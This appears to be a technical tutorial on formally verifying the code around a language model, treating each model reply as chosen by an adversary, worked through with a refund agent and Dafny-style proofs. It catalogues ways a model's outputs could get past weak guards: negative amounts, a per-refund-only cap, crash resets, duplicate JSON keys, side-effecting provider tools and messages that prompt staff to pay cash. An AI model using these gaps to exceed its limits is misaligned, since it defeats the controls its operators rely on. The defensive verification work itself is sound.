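# Verifying language-model scaffolds against every possible model output

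## What is being verified, and why treat the model's output as arbitrary?

A language model takes in text and produces text. It cannot issue a refund, edit a file or look up an order by itself. An ordinary program around it, called the scaffold, assembles a prompt, sends it to the model, reads the reply and acts on it. Formal verification means proving mathematically that a program has some property in every possible execution, not just the tested ones. Its methods apply to scaffolds because scaffolds are programs, but nobody can predict what the call to the model will return. One way to handle this is to assume nothing about the reply and require the proof to hold even if an opponent chooses it.

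Definitions of "scaffold" vary. The *International AI Safety Report 2026* (2026) defines it loosely, as roughly any additional software that helps a model perform a task. *SIA* (2026), a paper on self-improving agents, is more exact and counts "every part of the agent that is fixed code rather than model output". This includes the standing instructions at the top of each prompt, the code that parses the model's tool requests and routes them to the right handler, and the code that extracts a final answer. Many people say "harness" instead. In *Towards Portable Specification of the Agent Harness*, Gertler, Novelli and Floridi (2026) report that some authors use "scaffold" for what developers assemble before a run and "harness" for the software that executes it, but they find that the distinction does not hold in practice. They exclude from the harness the model's weights, its training data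 and whatever the agent acts upon, such as a codebase.

A model's performance can depend heavily on this layer. Gertler and colleagues cite a test of 50 coding tasks on which Claude Opus 4.5 scored 2% in one harness and 12% in another. They also point out that coding agents now write parts of their own harness. A proof is about a fixed program text, so if the agent rewrites that text, the proof no longer applies to what is running.

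A model call returns a string to the scaffold. *SEVerA* (Banerjee, Xu and colleagues, 2026) defines a language model as a function from $\Sigma^*$ to $\Sigma^{\leq n}$, that is, from prompts of any length to strings of at most $n$ characters. The model computes probabilities for the next character (in practice a token, a short chunk of text), a decoding step draws one, and the process repeats until it reaches an end marker or the length limit. The scaffold then has to interpret the string. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) presents a small programming language for agents in which a call adds the prompt to the conversation, samples a reply and parses it into either a value or an error message. A proof has to cover the error case too, since a reply may break off at the length limit or be a refusal where the program needed a number.

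### A refund agent

Suppose a shop lets an agent handle complaints. The agent may pay a customer at most 100 in total and may call the model at most three times per complaint.

```
paid := 0;  calls := 0;  answered := false
while calls < 3 and not answered:
    calls := calls + 1
    r := parse(model(history))        # the model call
    if r = Refund(x):
        if paid + x <= 100:           # the guard
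            pay(x);  paid := paid + x
    else if r = Reply(text):
        send(text);  answered := true
    history := history + r            # an error does only this
```

The parser turns each reply into `Refund(x)`, `Reply(text)` or an error, and it accepts `Refund(x)` only if `x` is a whole number, zero or more. If it accepted negative amounts, a reply of `Refund(-50)` would lower `paid` and make room for another 50 later. If the payment service ignored negative amounts, the customer would then end up with 150. An opponent would find this reply immediately, even though a sensible model would hardly ever write it.

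If a prompt instruction never to refund more than 100 replaces the guard, we can no longer prove that the program respects the limit, because the model could return the string `Refund(5000)` and the program would pay it. The instruction might work for months, but it might not. Banerjee and colleagues cite earlier work in which unconstrained agents broke rules on matters such as refund eligibility in 68–76% of interactions.

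### Why not verify the model itself?

The obvious alternative is to prove that the model never outputs a request for too much. One obstacle is size. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, there are $10^{2500}$ possible replies of 500 tokens, and the model selects among them by arithmetic on billions of learned numbers that no person wrote or can read as rules. *BEAVER* (2025) notes that researchers generally consider sound verification of language models infeasible at this scale, but makes some progress by computing guaranteed bounds on the probability that the reply to a given prompt satisfies a checkable property. This method needs access to the model's weights and handles only one prompt at a time, while the refund agent builds a new prompt for every customer.

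It is also hard to specify what to prove, because the requirements on a good reply (honest, helpful, in line with shop policy) exist only in natural language. Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, reviewed 38 studies and concluded that specification is the bottleneck. On one benchmark for translating descriptions into a formal planning language, GPT-4o produced well-formed output 96.1% of the time, but only 24.8% of its translations preserved the description's meaning. The best fine-tuned model reached 34.2%. Those are old models and a narrow task, so the exact figures may not carry over. But better translators would not remove the underlying problem, because a proof about a mistranslated rule looks exactly like a proof about the right one.

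Undecidability is also an obstacle. By Rice's theorem, no algorithm can correctly answer a non-trivial question about behaviour for every program in a general-purpose language, and *LLMs versus the Halting Problem* (2026) states this result for central verification tasks. Amer, Kinczel and Long (2026) point out in *No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* that idealised language models with unbounded context or external memory can have the same computing power as such a language. The theorem does not apply to a deployed model with finite memory, but the prover still has to deal with the problem of size.

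So the prover changes the statement. Write $S(r_1, r_2, r_3)$ for what the scaffold does when the three calls return $r_1$, $r_2$ and $r_3$, and $\varphi$ for the property wanted. The claim to prove is

$$\text{for all } r_1, r_2, r_3 \in \Sigma^{\leq n}: \quad S(r_1, r_2, r_3) \text{ satisfies } \varphi.$$

The model's actual replies are among those strings, so the property holds for them too, as long as the model can affect the world only through its replies. Because the model itself is not in the formula, the proof still holds for a new model version, after further training, or when a customer hides instructions in a complaint. The specification is also easier to write, since `paid <= 100` is a statement about a program variable and does not have to be translated from English. But the proof does not show that the replies are good, so the refund may still go to somebody who did not deserve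 it.

Moving the proof to the scaffold does not make it automatic. A scaffold in unrestricted Python can be any program, and *Intent-Driven Computing* (McCann, 2026) lists "This agent stays within its refund limit" among the properties that Rice's theorem makes undecidable for arbitrary programs. *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program* (Pérez-Acle, 2026) describes a program that searches the even numbers above 2 for one that is not the sum of two primes, and performs a forbidden action only if it finds one. The program is safe if and only if Goldbach's conjecture, an open problem in number theory, is true. Monitoring it would reveal a violation if one occurred, but could not show that none ever will.

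This limits only methods that must work for every program, so one particular scaffold can still be proved correct. Amer and colleagues make the same point about verified operating-system kernels. Restricting the program also helps. With a fixed limit on the number of steps, everything becomes decidable, although Pérez-Acle proves that a checker that is always right must take essentially that many steps on some programs. The refund agent is far too small for these limits to matter. Its loop runs at most three times, and `calls`, `paid` and `answered` can take at most 4 × 101 × 2 = 808 combinations of values (no test in the program reads `history`).

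### Runs, safety and liveness

A state is a snapshot of the program: the value of every variable, plus the place the program has reached. For the refund agent it is enough to look at the start of each pass through the loop and write down `calls`, `paid` and `answered`. A run is a sequence of states that begins at the start of the program and in which each state follows from the one before by a step of the program. If the replies are `Refund(60)`, `Refund(50)` and then a `Reply`, the run is

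(0, 0, no) → (1, 60, no) → (2, 60, no) → (3, 60, yes).

The guard blocks the second request because 60 + 50 is over the cap, so only the call counter changes. Other replies from the model would produce other runs, and a verifier has to account for all of them.

"The total paid never exceeds 100" is a safety property, which means that any violation is visible after finitely many steps. Amer and colleagues formalize this with a set, Bad, of finite action sequences. The empty sequence is not in Bad, and every continuation of a sequence in Bad is also in Bad. For the refund agent, Bad contains every sequence in which the payments so far add up to more than 100. The second condition reflects that nothing the agent does later can undo a violation. Because violations occur within finitely many steps, a failed proof can come with a finite list of replies that pushes the total above 100, which a developer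 can use as evidence.

"The customer eventually gets an answer" is a liveness property because it requires something wanted to happen at some point but sets no deadline. A finite stretch of silence does not refute it, since the answer might come at the next step. Allegrini, Shreekumar and Celik (2025) give a similar pair of properties for an automated financial planner in *Formalizing the Safety, Security, and Functional Properties of Agentic AI Systems*. The planner must not invest before it has calculated the risk (safety), and every request must eventually get a response (liveness).

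The refund agent is a slightly odd case because its three-call limit means a failure shows up after finitely many steps. Once the loop has ended without a `Reply`, no answer will ever come. The property is still a liveness property, because the classification considers all sequences of states, not just those this program can produce. Without `calls < 3`, the failing run would go on forever, and an observer could never say at any point that it had failed.

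### Demonic, angelic and random choice

The program text does not determine which reply the model returns. Whether a property holds can depend on what we assume about that reply, so we have to choose the assumption before we can verify the property.

With demonic choice, an opponent picks the model's output, so a property must hold for every possible output. Mamouras (2016), in *Synthesis of Strategies Using the Hoare Logic of Angelic and Demonic Nondeterminism*, uses demonic choice for influences outside the program's control, including human users, who "may choose to behave as an adversary". The cap on refunds holds under demonic choice. The opponent can return `Refund(x)` for any `x`, but the guard allows the payment only if the new total is at most 100, and the other two kinds of reply don't change `paid`. The customer is not guaranteed an answer, however, because the opponent can return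 gibberish three times, which ends the loop in state (3, 0, no) with no answer sent.

Under angelic choice, a helper on the prover's side chooses the model's outputs, and a property holds if some choice of them satisfies it. We can then prove that the customer gets an answer, because the first output could be a `Reply`. But we can also prove that the cap holds with the guard deleted, because the model could ask for 50 and nothing more. Angelic choice is therefore the wrong reading for a safety claim about a model. In Mamouras's account, it is meant for details that a programmer has left open and can still settle in the program's favour. He also combines the two kinds of choice, so that a program is correct if the helper has a strategy that works whatever the opponent does.

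Some current work on agents assumes something close to angelic choice. *Lean4Agent* (2026), which checks agent workflows, explicitly assumes that a model step whose preconditions hold "can produce" a result that meets its postconditions. Under that assumption, each step in a workflow that passes would supply what the next one needs, but a real model may still return something else.

Random choice draws the reply from a probability distribution, which is closest to what a model does. In the calculus of Garby and colleagues, each reply comes from the model's distribution given the conversation so far, so properties hold with some probability. If each of the three calls had a 90% chance of yielding a `Reply`, regardless of what happened before, the customer would go unanswered with probability 0.1³, or one time in a thousand. But the 90% figure needs a justification, and the assumption that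 earlier events don't affect it is doubtful when all three calls share one conversation. A hostile customer can also shift the distribution. The demonic proof of the cap doesn't use probabilities. It shows that no run exceeds 100, so the probability of exceeding 100 is zero under every distribution.

### The idea in current use

Treating the model this way is a recognised technique. Dantas and colleagues describe verification systems that define a state machine in advance, "with the LLM embedded as a non-deterministic oracle", meaning a component that may return any of several results, with no probabilities assigned to them. Their example is AgentVerify, which checks rules on memory, tool calls and human approval. They also list AgentVerify among the studies at high risk of bias, so it is stronger evidence that people use the technique than that the technique works well on large systems.

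Other systems build on the same idea. *TraceFix* (Xia, Li and colleagues, 2026) writes a model's decisions as either/or branches and has a checker explore every branch, however unlikely. SEVerA, by Banerjee and colleagues, gives each model call a contract that holds for any setting of the model's parameters. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) calls the model an adversary, and describes this as the strongest position available to a method that does not depend on the model's internals. It would reserve formal proof for the few skills that can do serious damage, including payment.

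## How does a proof handle a call that may return anything?

The claim to prove about the refund agent begins "for all $r_1, r_2, r_3$", and each call has about $10^{2500}$ possible replies, too many to check one by one. The prover instead works with formulas, starting from the condition wanted at the end of the program and moving backwards to compute what must be true before each statement. The step for a model call covers all possible replies at once.

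*Angelic Processes* (Ribeiro, 2014) traces the method to Floyd, who in 1967 attached conditions to the entries and exits of commands in a flowchart, and to Hoare, who gave proof rules for program text. *Guarded commands, non-determinacy and formal derivation of programs* (Dijkstra, 1975) turned the method into a calculation. For a program $S$ and a condition $Q$, it defines the weakest precondition $wp(S, Q)$, which holds in exactly those starting states from which $S$ is certain to terminate with $Q$ true. Hoare's preconditions ruled out a wrong result but did not guarantee that the program would terminate.

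The refund agent contains the line `paid := paid + x`. For the condition `paid <= 100` to hold after this line runs, `paid + x <= 100` must hold before it. This weakest precondition, found by substituting `paid + x` for `paid` in the condition, is the agent's guard. Dijkstra derived guards the same way. He chose an assignment, computed its weakest precondition, and let the assignment run only where that precondition held.

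### The rules

| Command | Weakest precondition for $Q$ | In words |
|---|---|---|
| `skip` | $Q$ | Nothing changes, so $Q$ must hold already. |
| `x := E` | $Q$ with $E$ in place of $x$ | $Q$ must hold for the new value. |
| `S; T` | $wp(S, wp(T, Q))$ | $S$ must end in a state from which $T$ achieves $Q$. |
| `if B then S else T` | $(B \Rightarrow wp(S,Q)) \wedge (\neg B \Rightarrow wp(T,Q))$ | The branch that runs must achieve $Q$. |
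| demonic choice of `S` or `T` | $wp(S,Q) \wedge wp(T,Q)$ | Both must achieve $Q$, since the opponent picks. |
| angelic choice of `S` or `T` | $wp(S,Q) \vee wp(T,Q)$ | One is enough, since the prover's side picks. |
| `havoc x` | $\forall x.\, Q$ | $Q$ must hold for every value of $x$. |
| `assert A` | $A \wedge Q$ | $A$ must hold, and so must $Q$. |
| `assume A` | $A \Rightarrow Q$ | $Q$ must hold wherever $A$ does. |

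The rules down to the conditional come from Dijkstra, and his conditional already contains demonic choice. Its guards may overlap, and if more than one is true, any of the corresponding alternatives may run. He wanted to leave open choices that didn't matter, such as which of two equal numbers to call the maximum, not to model an opponent. He admitted to "a considerable mental resistance" to programs that don't behave the same way twice.

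*Refinement Calculus* (Back and von Wright, 1997) treats a program as a game between an angel, on the prover's side, and a demon, its opponent. The demon may simply have different priorities, but since we cannot influence it, "we have to be prepared for the worst". The book also points out that a component whose behavior is fixed by hidden information still looks from outside as if it chooses freely. So the demonic rule suits a model with random sampling switched off just as well as one that samples, because the scaffold cannot see what produces the reply in either case.

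The `havoc` rule is the demonic rule with one alternative for each value. Back and von Wright give a more general command that assigns to $x$ any value $x'$ satisfying a condition $b$. Its weakest precondition is $\forall x'.\,(b \Rightarrow Q[x := x'])$, and if $b$ is "true", the command is `havoc x`. For the refund agent, $wp(\text{havoc } r,\ paid \leq 100)$ is just $paid \leq 100$, since the condition does not mention $r$. But $wp(\text{havoc } r,\ r \text{ is a Reply})$ is false in every state, because some values are not a `Reply`. If an angel chose $r$, "for all" would become "there is", and this precondition would be true.

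Dijkstra's calculus has $wp(S,P) \wedge wp(S,Q) = wp(S, P \wedge Q)$ for every program, so one can prove the refund cap and the limit on calls separately and then combine them. The corresponding law for "or" holds only for deterministic programs, and `havoc r` is nondeterministic. After it runs, $r$ is certain to be either a refund request or something else, but neither is certain by itself. The prover therefore cannot assume a particular kind of reply and has to show that the rest of the scaffold works for all of them.

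`assert` and `assume` both leave the state unchanged, but they differ when $A$ is false. Back and von Wright explain the difference in terms of contracts. If an assertion fails, our side has broken the contract and achieves nothing. If an assumption fails, our side is released from the contract and counts as having achieved $Q$. So $wp(\text{assume false}, Q)$ is true for every $Q$, and one false assumption lets us "prove" that an agent with no guard respects its cap. The literature calls `assume false` "magic", and no computer can execute it. Terminology varies, and *Calculating modules in contextual logic program refinement* (Colvin, Hayes and Strooper, 2006) uses "assumption" for a command that may abort when its condition is false, which verification tools call an assertion.

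Writing `havoc r; assume A` gives $\forall r.\,(A \Rightarrow Q)$, so the proof only has to cover replies that satisfy $A$. Code that checks replies before using them can justify this assumption.

### Why havoc can stand in for the model

These rules apply to a program that contains `havoc r`, but the shop runs a program that contains a model. Refinement connects the two. Morgan, Robinson and Gardiner (1988), in *On the Refinement Calculus*, say that $P$ is refined by $M$, written $P \sqsubseteq M$, if

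$$wp(P, Q) \Rightarrow wp(M, Q) \quad \text{for every condition } Q.$$

Anything $P$ is certain to achieve, $M$ is certain to achieve too, so $M$ is an acceptable replacement for $P$.

Let $M$ be any command that always terminates and changes no variable except $r$. Then $\text{havoc } r \sqsubseteq M$. To prove this, suppose $wp(\text{havoc } r, Q)$ holds before $M$ runs, which means that $Q$ holds for every value of $r$ with the other variables as they are. When $M$ terminates, the other variables are unchanged and $r$ has some value $v$. Since $Q$ holds for every value of $r$, it holds for $v$. The proof doesn't depend on how $M$ produces $v$, so $M$ can be a language model, a die or a person typing.

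The converse is also true. `havoc r` always terminates, so anything that refines it must always terminate too. `havoc r` also leaves every variable except `r` unchanged, so a refinement must do the same. For example, if `paid` is 60 before the call, it must be 60 afterwards. Morgan and colleagues prove both directions as one theorem about their specification statement $w : [pre, post]$, which means "starting where $pre$ holds, change only $w$ and end where $post$ holds". In their notation `havoc r` is $r : [true, true]$. By this theorem, a model call refines `havoc r` exactly when it always returns, its value has the right type, and it changes nothing except `r`. The next section covers whether a call to a real service meets these requirements.

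The call sits inside a loop in a larger program, so the proof also has to show that refining a fragment refines the program around it. This follows from Morgan and colleagues' theorem that sequencing, conditionals and loops all preserve refinement. Therefore, if the agent is certain to respect the cap with `havoc r` in place of the model, it is also certain to respect the cap with the model.

### Deriving the refund cap

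This is the body of the agent's loop with the model call replaced and one assertion added:

```
calls := calls + 1
havoc r                            # was: parse(model(history))
if r = Refund(x):
    if paid + x <= 100:
        assert paid + x <= 100     # just before money moves
        pay(x);  paid := paid + x
else if r = Reply(text):
    send(text);  answered := true
history := history + r
```

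The assertion is part of the specification, so it is needed even though the program already has a guard. A weakest precondition describes only the final state, so without the assertion, an agent could overpay, later correct `paid`, and still pass. With the assertion, a program that makes even one forbidden payment cannot satisfy any postcondition.

Let $Q$ be `paid <= 100` and work upwards from the bottom. The last line does not change `paid`, so $Q$ passes through it unaltered. In the conditional, the cases are:

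- `Refund(x)` with `paid + x <= 100`. Going back through the assignment turns $Q$ into `paid + x <= 100`, and the assertion adds the same condition again. The guard supplies exactly this, so the case requires nothing further.
- `Refund(x)` with `paid + x > 100`. The agent pays nothing, so `paid <= 100` has to hold already.
- `Reply(text)` or an error. `paid` does not change, so again `paid <= 100` has to hold already.

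Next comes `havoc r`, which puts "for all $r$" in front:

$$\forall r.\ \begin{cases} paid + x \leq 100 & \text{if } r = \text{Refund}(x) \text{ and } paid + x \leq 100,\\ paid \leq 100 & \text{otherwise.}\end{cases}$$

The first line is always true because its condition implies its conclusion. The second applies to at least one reply, such as an error, so the whole formula reduces to $paid \leq 100$. Incrementing `calls` does not affect it. So the weakest precondition of the loop body for `paid <= 100` is `paid <= 100` itself, and one pass preserves the cap whatever the model returns.

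A condition that every pass preserves is a loop invariant. This one holds at the start, where `paid` is 0, so it holds after any number of passes. To show that the loop also ends, Dijkstra uses a variant, a whole-number expression that is never negative while the loop is running and that falls by at least 1 on every pass. Under demonic choice, the invariant must hold and the variant must fall whatever the reply. `3 - calls` works as a variant because no reply can change `calls`. The number of questions still unanswered would not work, because a gibberish reply could leave it unchanged. Dijkstra's loop theorem then guarantees that, provided `pay` and `send` return, the agent terminates with `paid <= 100` and with either three calls made or an answer sent.

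The proof concerns only the variable `paid`, which can differ from the money that really leaves the shop. The derivation above would still succeed if the parser let negative amounts through, since it never used $x \geq 0$. A reply of `Refund(-50)` could then lower `paid` without any money coming back to the shop, as in the earlier example. The proof can catch this with an extra variable, `sent`, which exists only for the proof and counts the money that really leaves the shop. Each `pay(x)` raises `sent` by the larger of `x` and 0, and the invariant becomes `sent = paid and paid <= 100`. The paying case now also requires that the larger of `x` and 0 equal `x`, which is true only if `x` is not negative, so the proof succeeds with the strict parser and fails without it.

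### A faulty guard

Suppose a programmer writes `if x <= 100` in place of `if paid + x <= 100`. This limits each refund and forgets about the total. Only the first case of the derivation changes, and it now requires

$$\forall x \geq 0.\ (x \leq 100 \Rightarrow paid + x \leq 100).$$

The strictest case is $x = 100$, which requires `paid` to be 0. The weakest precondition of one pass therefore narrows from `paid <= 100` to `paid = 0`. The invariant does not imply `paid = 0`, so the proof cannot continue.

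Going back one more pass leads to a counterexample. For two passes to be safe, the first must be certain to end with `paid = 0`, and it isn't, because the opponent can ask for any positive amount up to 100. The weakest precondition for two passes is therefore false in every state. To read off the replies, pick a first amount that makes `paid` positive, say 60, and then a second amount that passes the guard and breaks the cap, say 60 again. The run, written as (`calls`, `paid`, `answered`), is

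(0, 0, no) → (1, 60, no) → (2, 120, no).

Of the 10,201 pairs of amounts between 0 and 100, about half (5,050) add up to more than 100. Still, tests with only one refund per complaint would never find the fault, and a well-behaved model might go a long time without triggering it.

An invariant proof can also fail when the program has no bug. Suppose the guard is instead `calls = 1 and x <= 100`, which allows a payment on the first call only. This agent respects the cap, but the proof of `paid <= 100` still fails. The invariant permits a state with `calls = 0` and `paid = 60`, which the agent can never reach, and a refund of 60 from there brings `paid` to 120. Adding "if `calls` is 0 then `paid` is 0" to the invariant makes the proof work. The two refunds of 60 should therefore be reported as a fault only after checking that they start from the program's real initial state, which they do.

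### When the set of replies is infinite

Dijkstra defined the meaning of a loop by counting passes. Let $H_k(Q)$ be the weakest precondition for the loop to end within $k$ passes with $Q$ true. Then the weakest precondition of the loop is that $H_k(Q)$ holds for some $k$. For the refund agent, $k = 3$ is enough.

A scaffold might ask the model how many documents to read, get a whole number $n$ and read $n$ documents. Every run ends, because every $n$ is finite. But no $k$ fixed before the call covers all the values of $n$, so by Dijkstra's definition this program is not certain to terminate. His *On non-determinacy being bounded* discusses a similar loop, which counts $x$ down to 0 when $x$ is positive and, when $x$ is negative, first sets it to "any positive integer". His formula gives $x \geq 0$ as the precondition for termination, although the loop would also end from negative values.

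The property that fails is continuity. Take conditions $C_0, C_1, C_2, \ldots$, each implying the next. A command $S$ is continuous if

$$wp(S,\ \exists r.\, C_r) = \exists s.\ wp(S, C_s).$$

In other words, if $S$ is certain to end in some member of the growing sequence, then we can name in advance one member in which it is certain to end. This fails when $S$ is `havoc x` over the natural numbers and $C_r$ is the condition $x < r$. Every number is smaller than some $r$, so the left side is true, but no single $s$ exceeds every number, so the right side is false.

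Dijkstra (1982), in *The equivalence of bounded nondeterminacy and continuity*, proves that each property implies the other, with an argument he credits to Scholten. If some $S$ is not continuous, a program can run $S$ and then set $x$ to the smallest $k$ for which $C_k$ holds. From some starting states, this program always gives $x$ a value, but no upper bound on that value is guaranteed. So whenever continuity fails, there is an unbounded choice.

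Dijkstra concluded that no program can "set x to any positive integer", since a machine would have to choose among infinitely many possibilities in finite time. Boom (1978), in *A weaker precondition for loops*, replied that the problem was in the loop rule. An arbitrary integer can represent a design decision not yet made, such as the page size of a planned computer system, and no machine has to make an infinite choice at run time. Boom repaired the rule by letting $k$ range over the ordinals, which extend the natural numbers to include infinite values. For the document-reading scaffold, $k$ is the first infinite ordinal, $\omega$, before the model replies and a finite number afterwards. Back and von Wright agree with Boom and call continuity "much overrated as a semantic restriction".

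For language models the dispute hardly matters, because replies have a length limit. A model adds tokens until it stops, much like Dijkstra's first attempt at a program that chooses "any positive integer". His loop starts with $x$ at 1, and each pass either adds 1 to $x$ or ends the loop. It runs forever if an opponent always chooses to add. Dijkstra's second version allows the addition only while $x < N$ for some large constant $N$, so it always terminates and the choice is finite. A token limit has the same effect as $N$. With a finite vocabulary and at most $n$ tokens there are only finitely many replies, so `havoc r` is an ordinary demonic choice among very many alternatives, and it is continuous. The bound may still be useless in practice, since a 500-digit reply can request nearly $10^{500}$ documents.

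The refund cap does not depend on termination. A second loop theorem of Dijkstra's needs only the invariant and leaves termination as a separate condition. Mamouras goes further and counts a run that never ends as correct. This definition is too weak to guarantee that the customer gets an answer, but it is enough for a rule about payments as long as an assertion guards each payment.

### In current verifiers

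Verification tools usually represent whole numbers as unbounded, whatever the token limit, because this simplifies the formulas. The infinite case therefore comes up in practice, and tools handle it with variants more flexible than a single number. Filliâtre's *An example from EWD 673* gives a complete program for the Why3 verifier, based on another of Dijkstra's notes. It declares a function `any_nat` with no body, whose result is guaranteed only to be at least 0. A loop then updates two counters, `x` and `y`. While `x` is positive, each pass lowers `x` by 1 and resets `y` to `any_nat()`. A pass also lowers `y` by 1 if `y` is positive. No single whole number can serve as the variant, because `y` may be reset to any value, however large. Filliâtre instead uses the pair `(x, y)`, compared like words in a dictionary. Each pass either lowers `x`, whatever happens to `y`, or keeps `x` at 0 and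 lowers `y`. Such a sequence of pairs cannot go on forever. An agent has the same structure if `x` is the number of model calls left and `y` is the amount of work the latest reply requires.

A function without a body is also the usual way to write a model call in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier. The refund agent might look like this:

```
datatype Msg = Refund(x: nat) | Reply(text: string) | Error

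method CallModel(history: seq<Msg>) returns (r: Msg)
  ensures true                     // no body, no promise

method Agent() {
  var paid, calls, answered := 0, 0, false;
  var history: seq<Msg> := [];
  while calls < 3 && !answered
    invariant paid <= 100
    decreases 3 - calls
  {
    calls := calls + 1;
    var r := CallModel(history);
    if r.Refund? {
      if paid + r.x <= 100 { paid := paid + r.x; }
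    } else if r.Reply? { answered := true; }
    history := history + [r];
  }
}
```

Dafny checks a caller using only the specification of the method it calls, so the method doesn't need a body. Because the postcondition is `true`, the proof can assume nothing about `r` except its type. The type `nat` represents the parser's rejection of negative amounts. Someone still has to check that the real parser rejects them, because Dafny assumes the declaration is correct.

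Dafny translates the program into Boogie, a simpler language made for verification, which has a `havoc` command. A method call becomes an `assert` of the method's precondition, a `havoc` of its result and an `assume` of its postcondition. For a loop, the verifier asserts the invariant on entry, applies `havoc` to every variable the loop changes, assumes the invariant and the loop test, runs the body once and asserts the invariant again. Because this pass starts from an arbitrary state that satisfies the invariant, it covers all passes. The false alarm about the state with `calls = 0` and `paid = 60` arises because, after the `havoc`, the verifier has no information about the changed variables except the invariant.

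*SV-LIB 1.0* (Beyer, Ernst and colleagues, 2025) lists Boogie and Why3 among the widely used verification languages and proposes a common format that different tools can read. The format also has `havoc`, in a part set aside for nondeterminism, and annotations for preconditions, postconditions, invariants and variants. A tool that reads the format reports "correct" or "incorrect" and can supply a witness, which is evidence that another tool can check. The witness may contain the loop invariants if the program is correct, and contains a concrete run if a safety property is violated. For the faulty refund agent, that run would include the two values that `havoc` gave to `r`. Beyer and colleagues distinguish this kind of witness from one for a failed invariant, because a witness for a failed invariant may follow a path that the program can never take.

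## When can a model call safely be replaced by an arbitrary value?

The refinement theorem treats a model call as one command that returns a value. A real call takes many steps on several machines. The scaffold opens a connection, a server generates tokens one at a time, packets travel back, and a parser turns the text into a value. To extend the proof about `havoc r` to real calls, we use a simulation argument, which matches the steps of the real system with steps of the program we verified.

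Call the running agent the real system and the program with `havoc r` the abstract system. For both, keep a list of the actions taken so far, meaning payments and messages to the customer. A simulation is a relation $\sim$ between real states $c$ and abstract states $a$ with these properties:

- For every starting state $c$ of the real system there is a starting state $a$ of the abstract system with $c \sim a$.
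- If $c \sim a$ and the real system can step from $c$ to $c'$, then the abstract system can get from $a$, in zero or more steps, to some $a'$ with $c' \sim a'$.
- If $c \sim a$, the two lists of actions are the same.

If a simulation exists, every safety property that holds for the abstract system's actions also holds for the real system's. The proof first establishes, by induction on $n$, that the real state after $n$ steps matches some state the abstract system can reach. The first property gives the case $n = 0$, and the second extends it from $n$ to $n + 1$. If a real run violated the safety property, the violation would be visible after finitely many steps, when the matching abstract state has the same list of actions. The abstract system could then violate the property too, which contradicts the proof about it. The argument does not cover liveness, because it relies on the violation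 having happened by some finite step.

For the refund agent, a real state matches an abstract one if both have the same variable values, place in the program and list of actions. The relation ignores everything else, such as half-finished replies, network traffic and the model's weights. While the server generates tokens, the abstract system takes no steps. When the parser delivers a value $v$, the abstract system executes `havoc r` and picks $v$. The abstract system also has runs that no real model would cause. These extra runs cannot make a successful proof wrong, but they can make a proof fail because of a reply that no real model would give.

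### Conditions on the real call

The second property is the harder one to establish because it covers every step of the real system, including steps nobody thought of when writing the abstract program. For a model call, it amounts to five conditions. If any of them fails, Dafny still accepts the refund agent, but the real agent may overpay or hang.

The type of `r` must include everything the call can produce, including network errors, refusals, replies cut off at the length limit and empty strings. Suppose we delete `Error` from the Dafny datatype, which makes the proof easier because it has fewer cases to cover. Suppose also that in the real system the first reply is `Refund(60)` and the second is an empty string. The parser raises an exception that nothing catches, the process crashes, and a supervisor program restarts the complaint with `paid` at 0. The next `Refund(60)` passes the guard,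 and the customer has received 120 in total. No abstract run contains a crash and a restart, so the simulation breaks at the empty string. *FCP* (Shashank, 2026), a system for checking AI-written software against the request behind it, avoids such gaps with a catch-all. When the checker calls a function, it records a code for the outcome. Each expected exception has its own code, another code covers any other exception or no answer within the time limit, and a last one covers return values of the wrong kind.

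The call must also have no effect other than returning a value, because the proof assumes that whatever was established about `paid` before the call still holds afterward. Some model providers run tools on their own servers. If the shop connects its payment account to such a tool, the model can pay out 500 while it composes a reply and then return the text "Done". The real list of actions then contains a payment that `havoc r` cannot produce. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* reduces this condition to one structural assumption, that the runtime can intercept every tool request before it reaches a host machine interface.

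People can also be a side channel. The refund agent may send the customer any text, including "show this message at the counter for 500 in cash". If the staff obey such messages, the shop loses 500 while `paid` stays at 0. The proven limit on the agent's payments therefore applies to the shop's total payments only if nobody else treats the agent's messages as orders.

The third condition is that the call returns or times out. If the server accepts a request and never answers, the agent hangs. The cap still holds, since a hanging agent pays nobody and the abstract system can match it by staying in the same state. But the earlier proof also showed that the agent finishes, and that part fails because the loop never reaches its next pass. A time limit fixes this, provided the scaffold turns an expired call into an `Error`.

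After a model call times out, its answer may still arrive. Suppose the first call's answer, `Refund(60)`, arrives during the second call. If the scaffold treats it as the second call's answer, this is harmless because `havoc r` allows any value there. But a leftover handler from the first call might act on it while the loop is processing another `Refund(60)`. The handler and the loop can then both check the guard while `paid` is still 0, and the customer gets 120. The scaffold has to discard late answers or send them through the same loop.

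The verified part must include the parser. The Dafny program applies `havoc` to a value that has already been parsed, so it assumes the parser is correct. This goes wrong with the parser that lets negative amounts through. It can also go wrong when two parsers read the same reply differently. Suppose the reply is in JSON, a common text format for data, and gives the amount twice, first as 60 and then as 600. Some JSON parsers keep the first value and some keep the last. If the guard's parser reads 60 and the scaffold forwards the original text to the payment service, the service may read 600 and pay it. A safer abstract program applies `havoc` to the raw string `s` and then runs `r := parse(s)`. The prover must show that `parse` returns a `Msg` for every string and has no side effects, and the rest of the scaffold may use only `r`, not `s`.

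*L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026) replaces a model call with an arbitrary value to verify one of the parsers in its agent runtime, which is written in the proof language Lean. A second model in the runtime reviews risky tool calls and judges them safe or "wild". The parser reads the verdict only from the first line that begins with "VERDICT:", and a Lean theorem states that any reply without such a line counts as wild.

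For agents, Shashank instead keeps a single copy of the scaffold's decision logic, written in a restricted subset of Python. The agent runs this code, and a translator turns it into a circuit for the model checker. The code and the circuit agreed on 6,000 random turns for each of ten scaffolds. This is good evidence that the translation is correct but doesn't prove it, so the link between the proof and the running program is weaker than the proof itself.

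Finally, the abstract choices must include everything the model can really do, even replies that a sensible model would not give. Shashank's figures for an assistant that handles an online store's returns under eleven rules show the danger of leaving such replies out. They cover ten scaffolds: a carefully guarded one, a plain loop that runs whatever the model requests, and eight copies of the guarded one with a one-line bug each. With the model's output left completely free, the guarded scaffold satisfied eight of the nine rules that could be checked, and the ninth conflicted with another rule. On the plain loop, the solver's first attack was a $406 refund in the first turn. Six of the eight bugs had no visible effect as long as the model followed the rules, so a proof that considered only rule-following replies would have passed all six. Ordinary trials would not have helped much either,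 because when three Claude models played the assistant for 82 turns, the guard never had to block a request.

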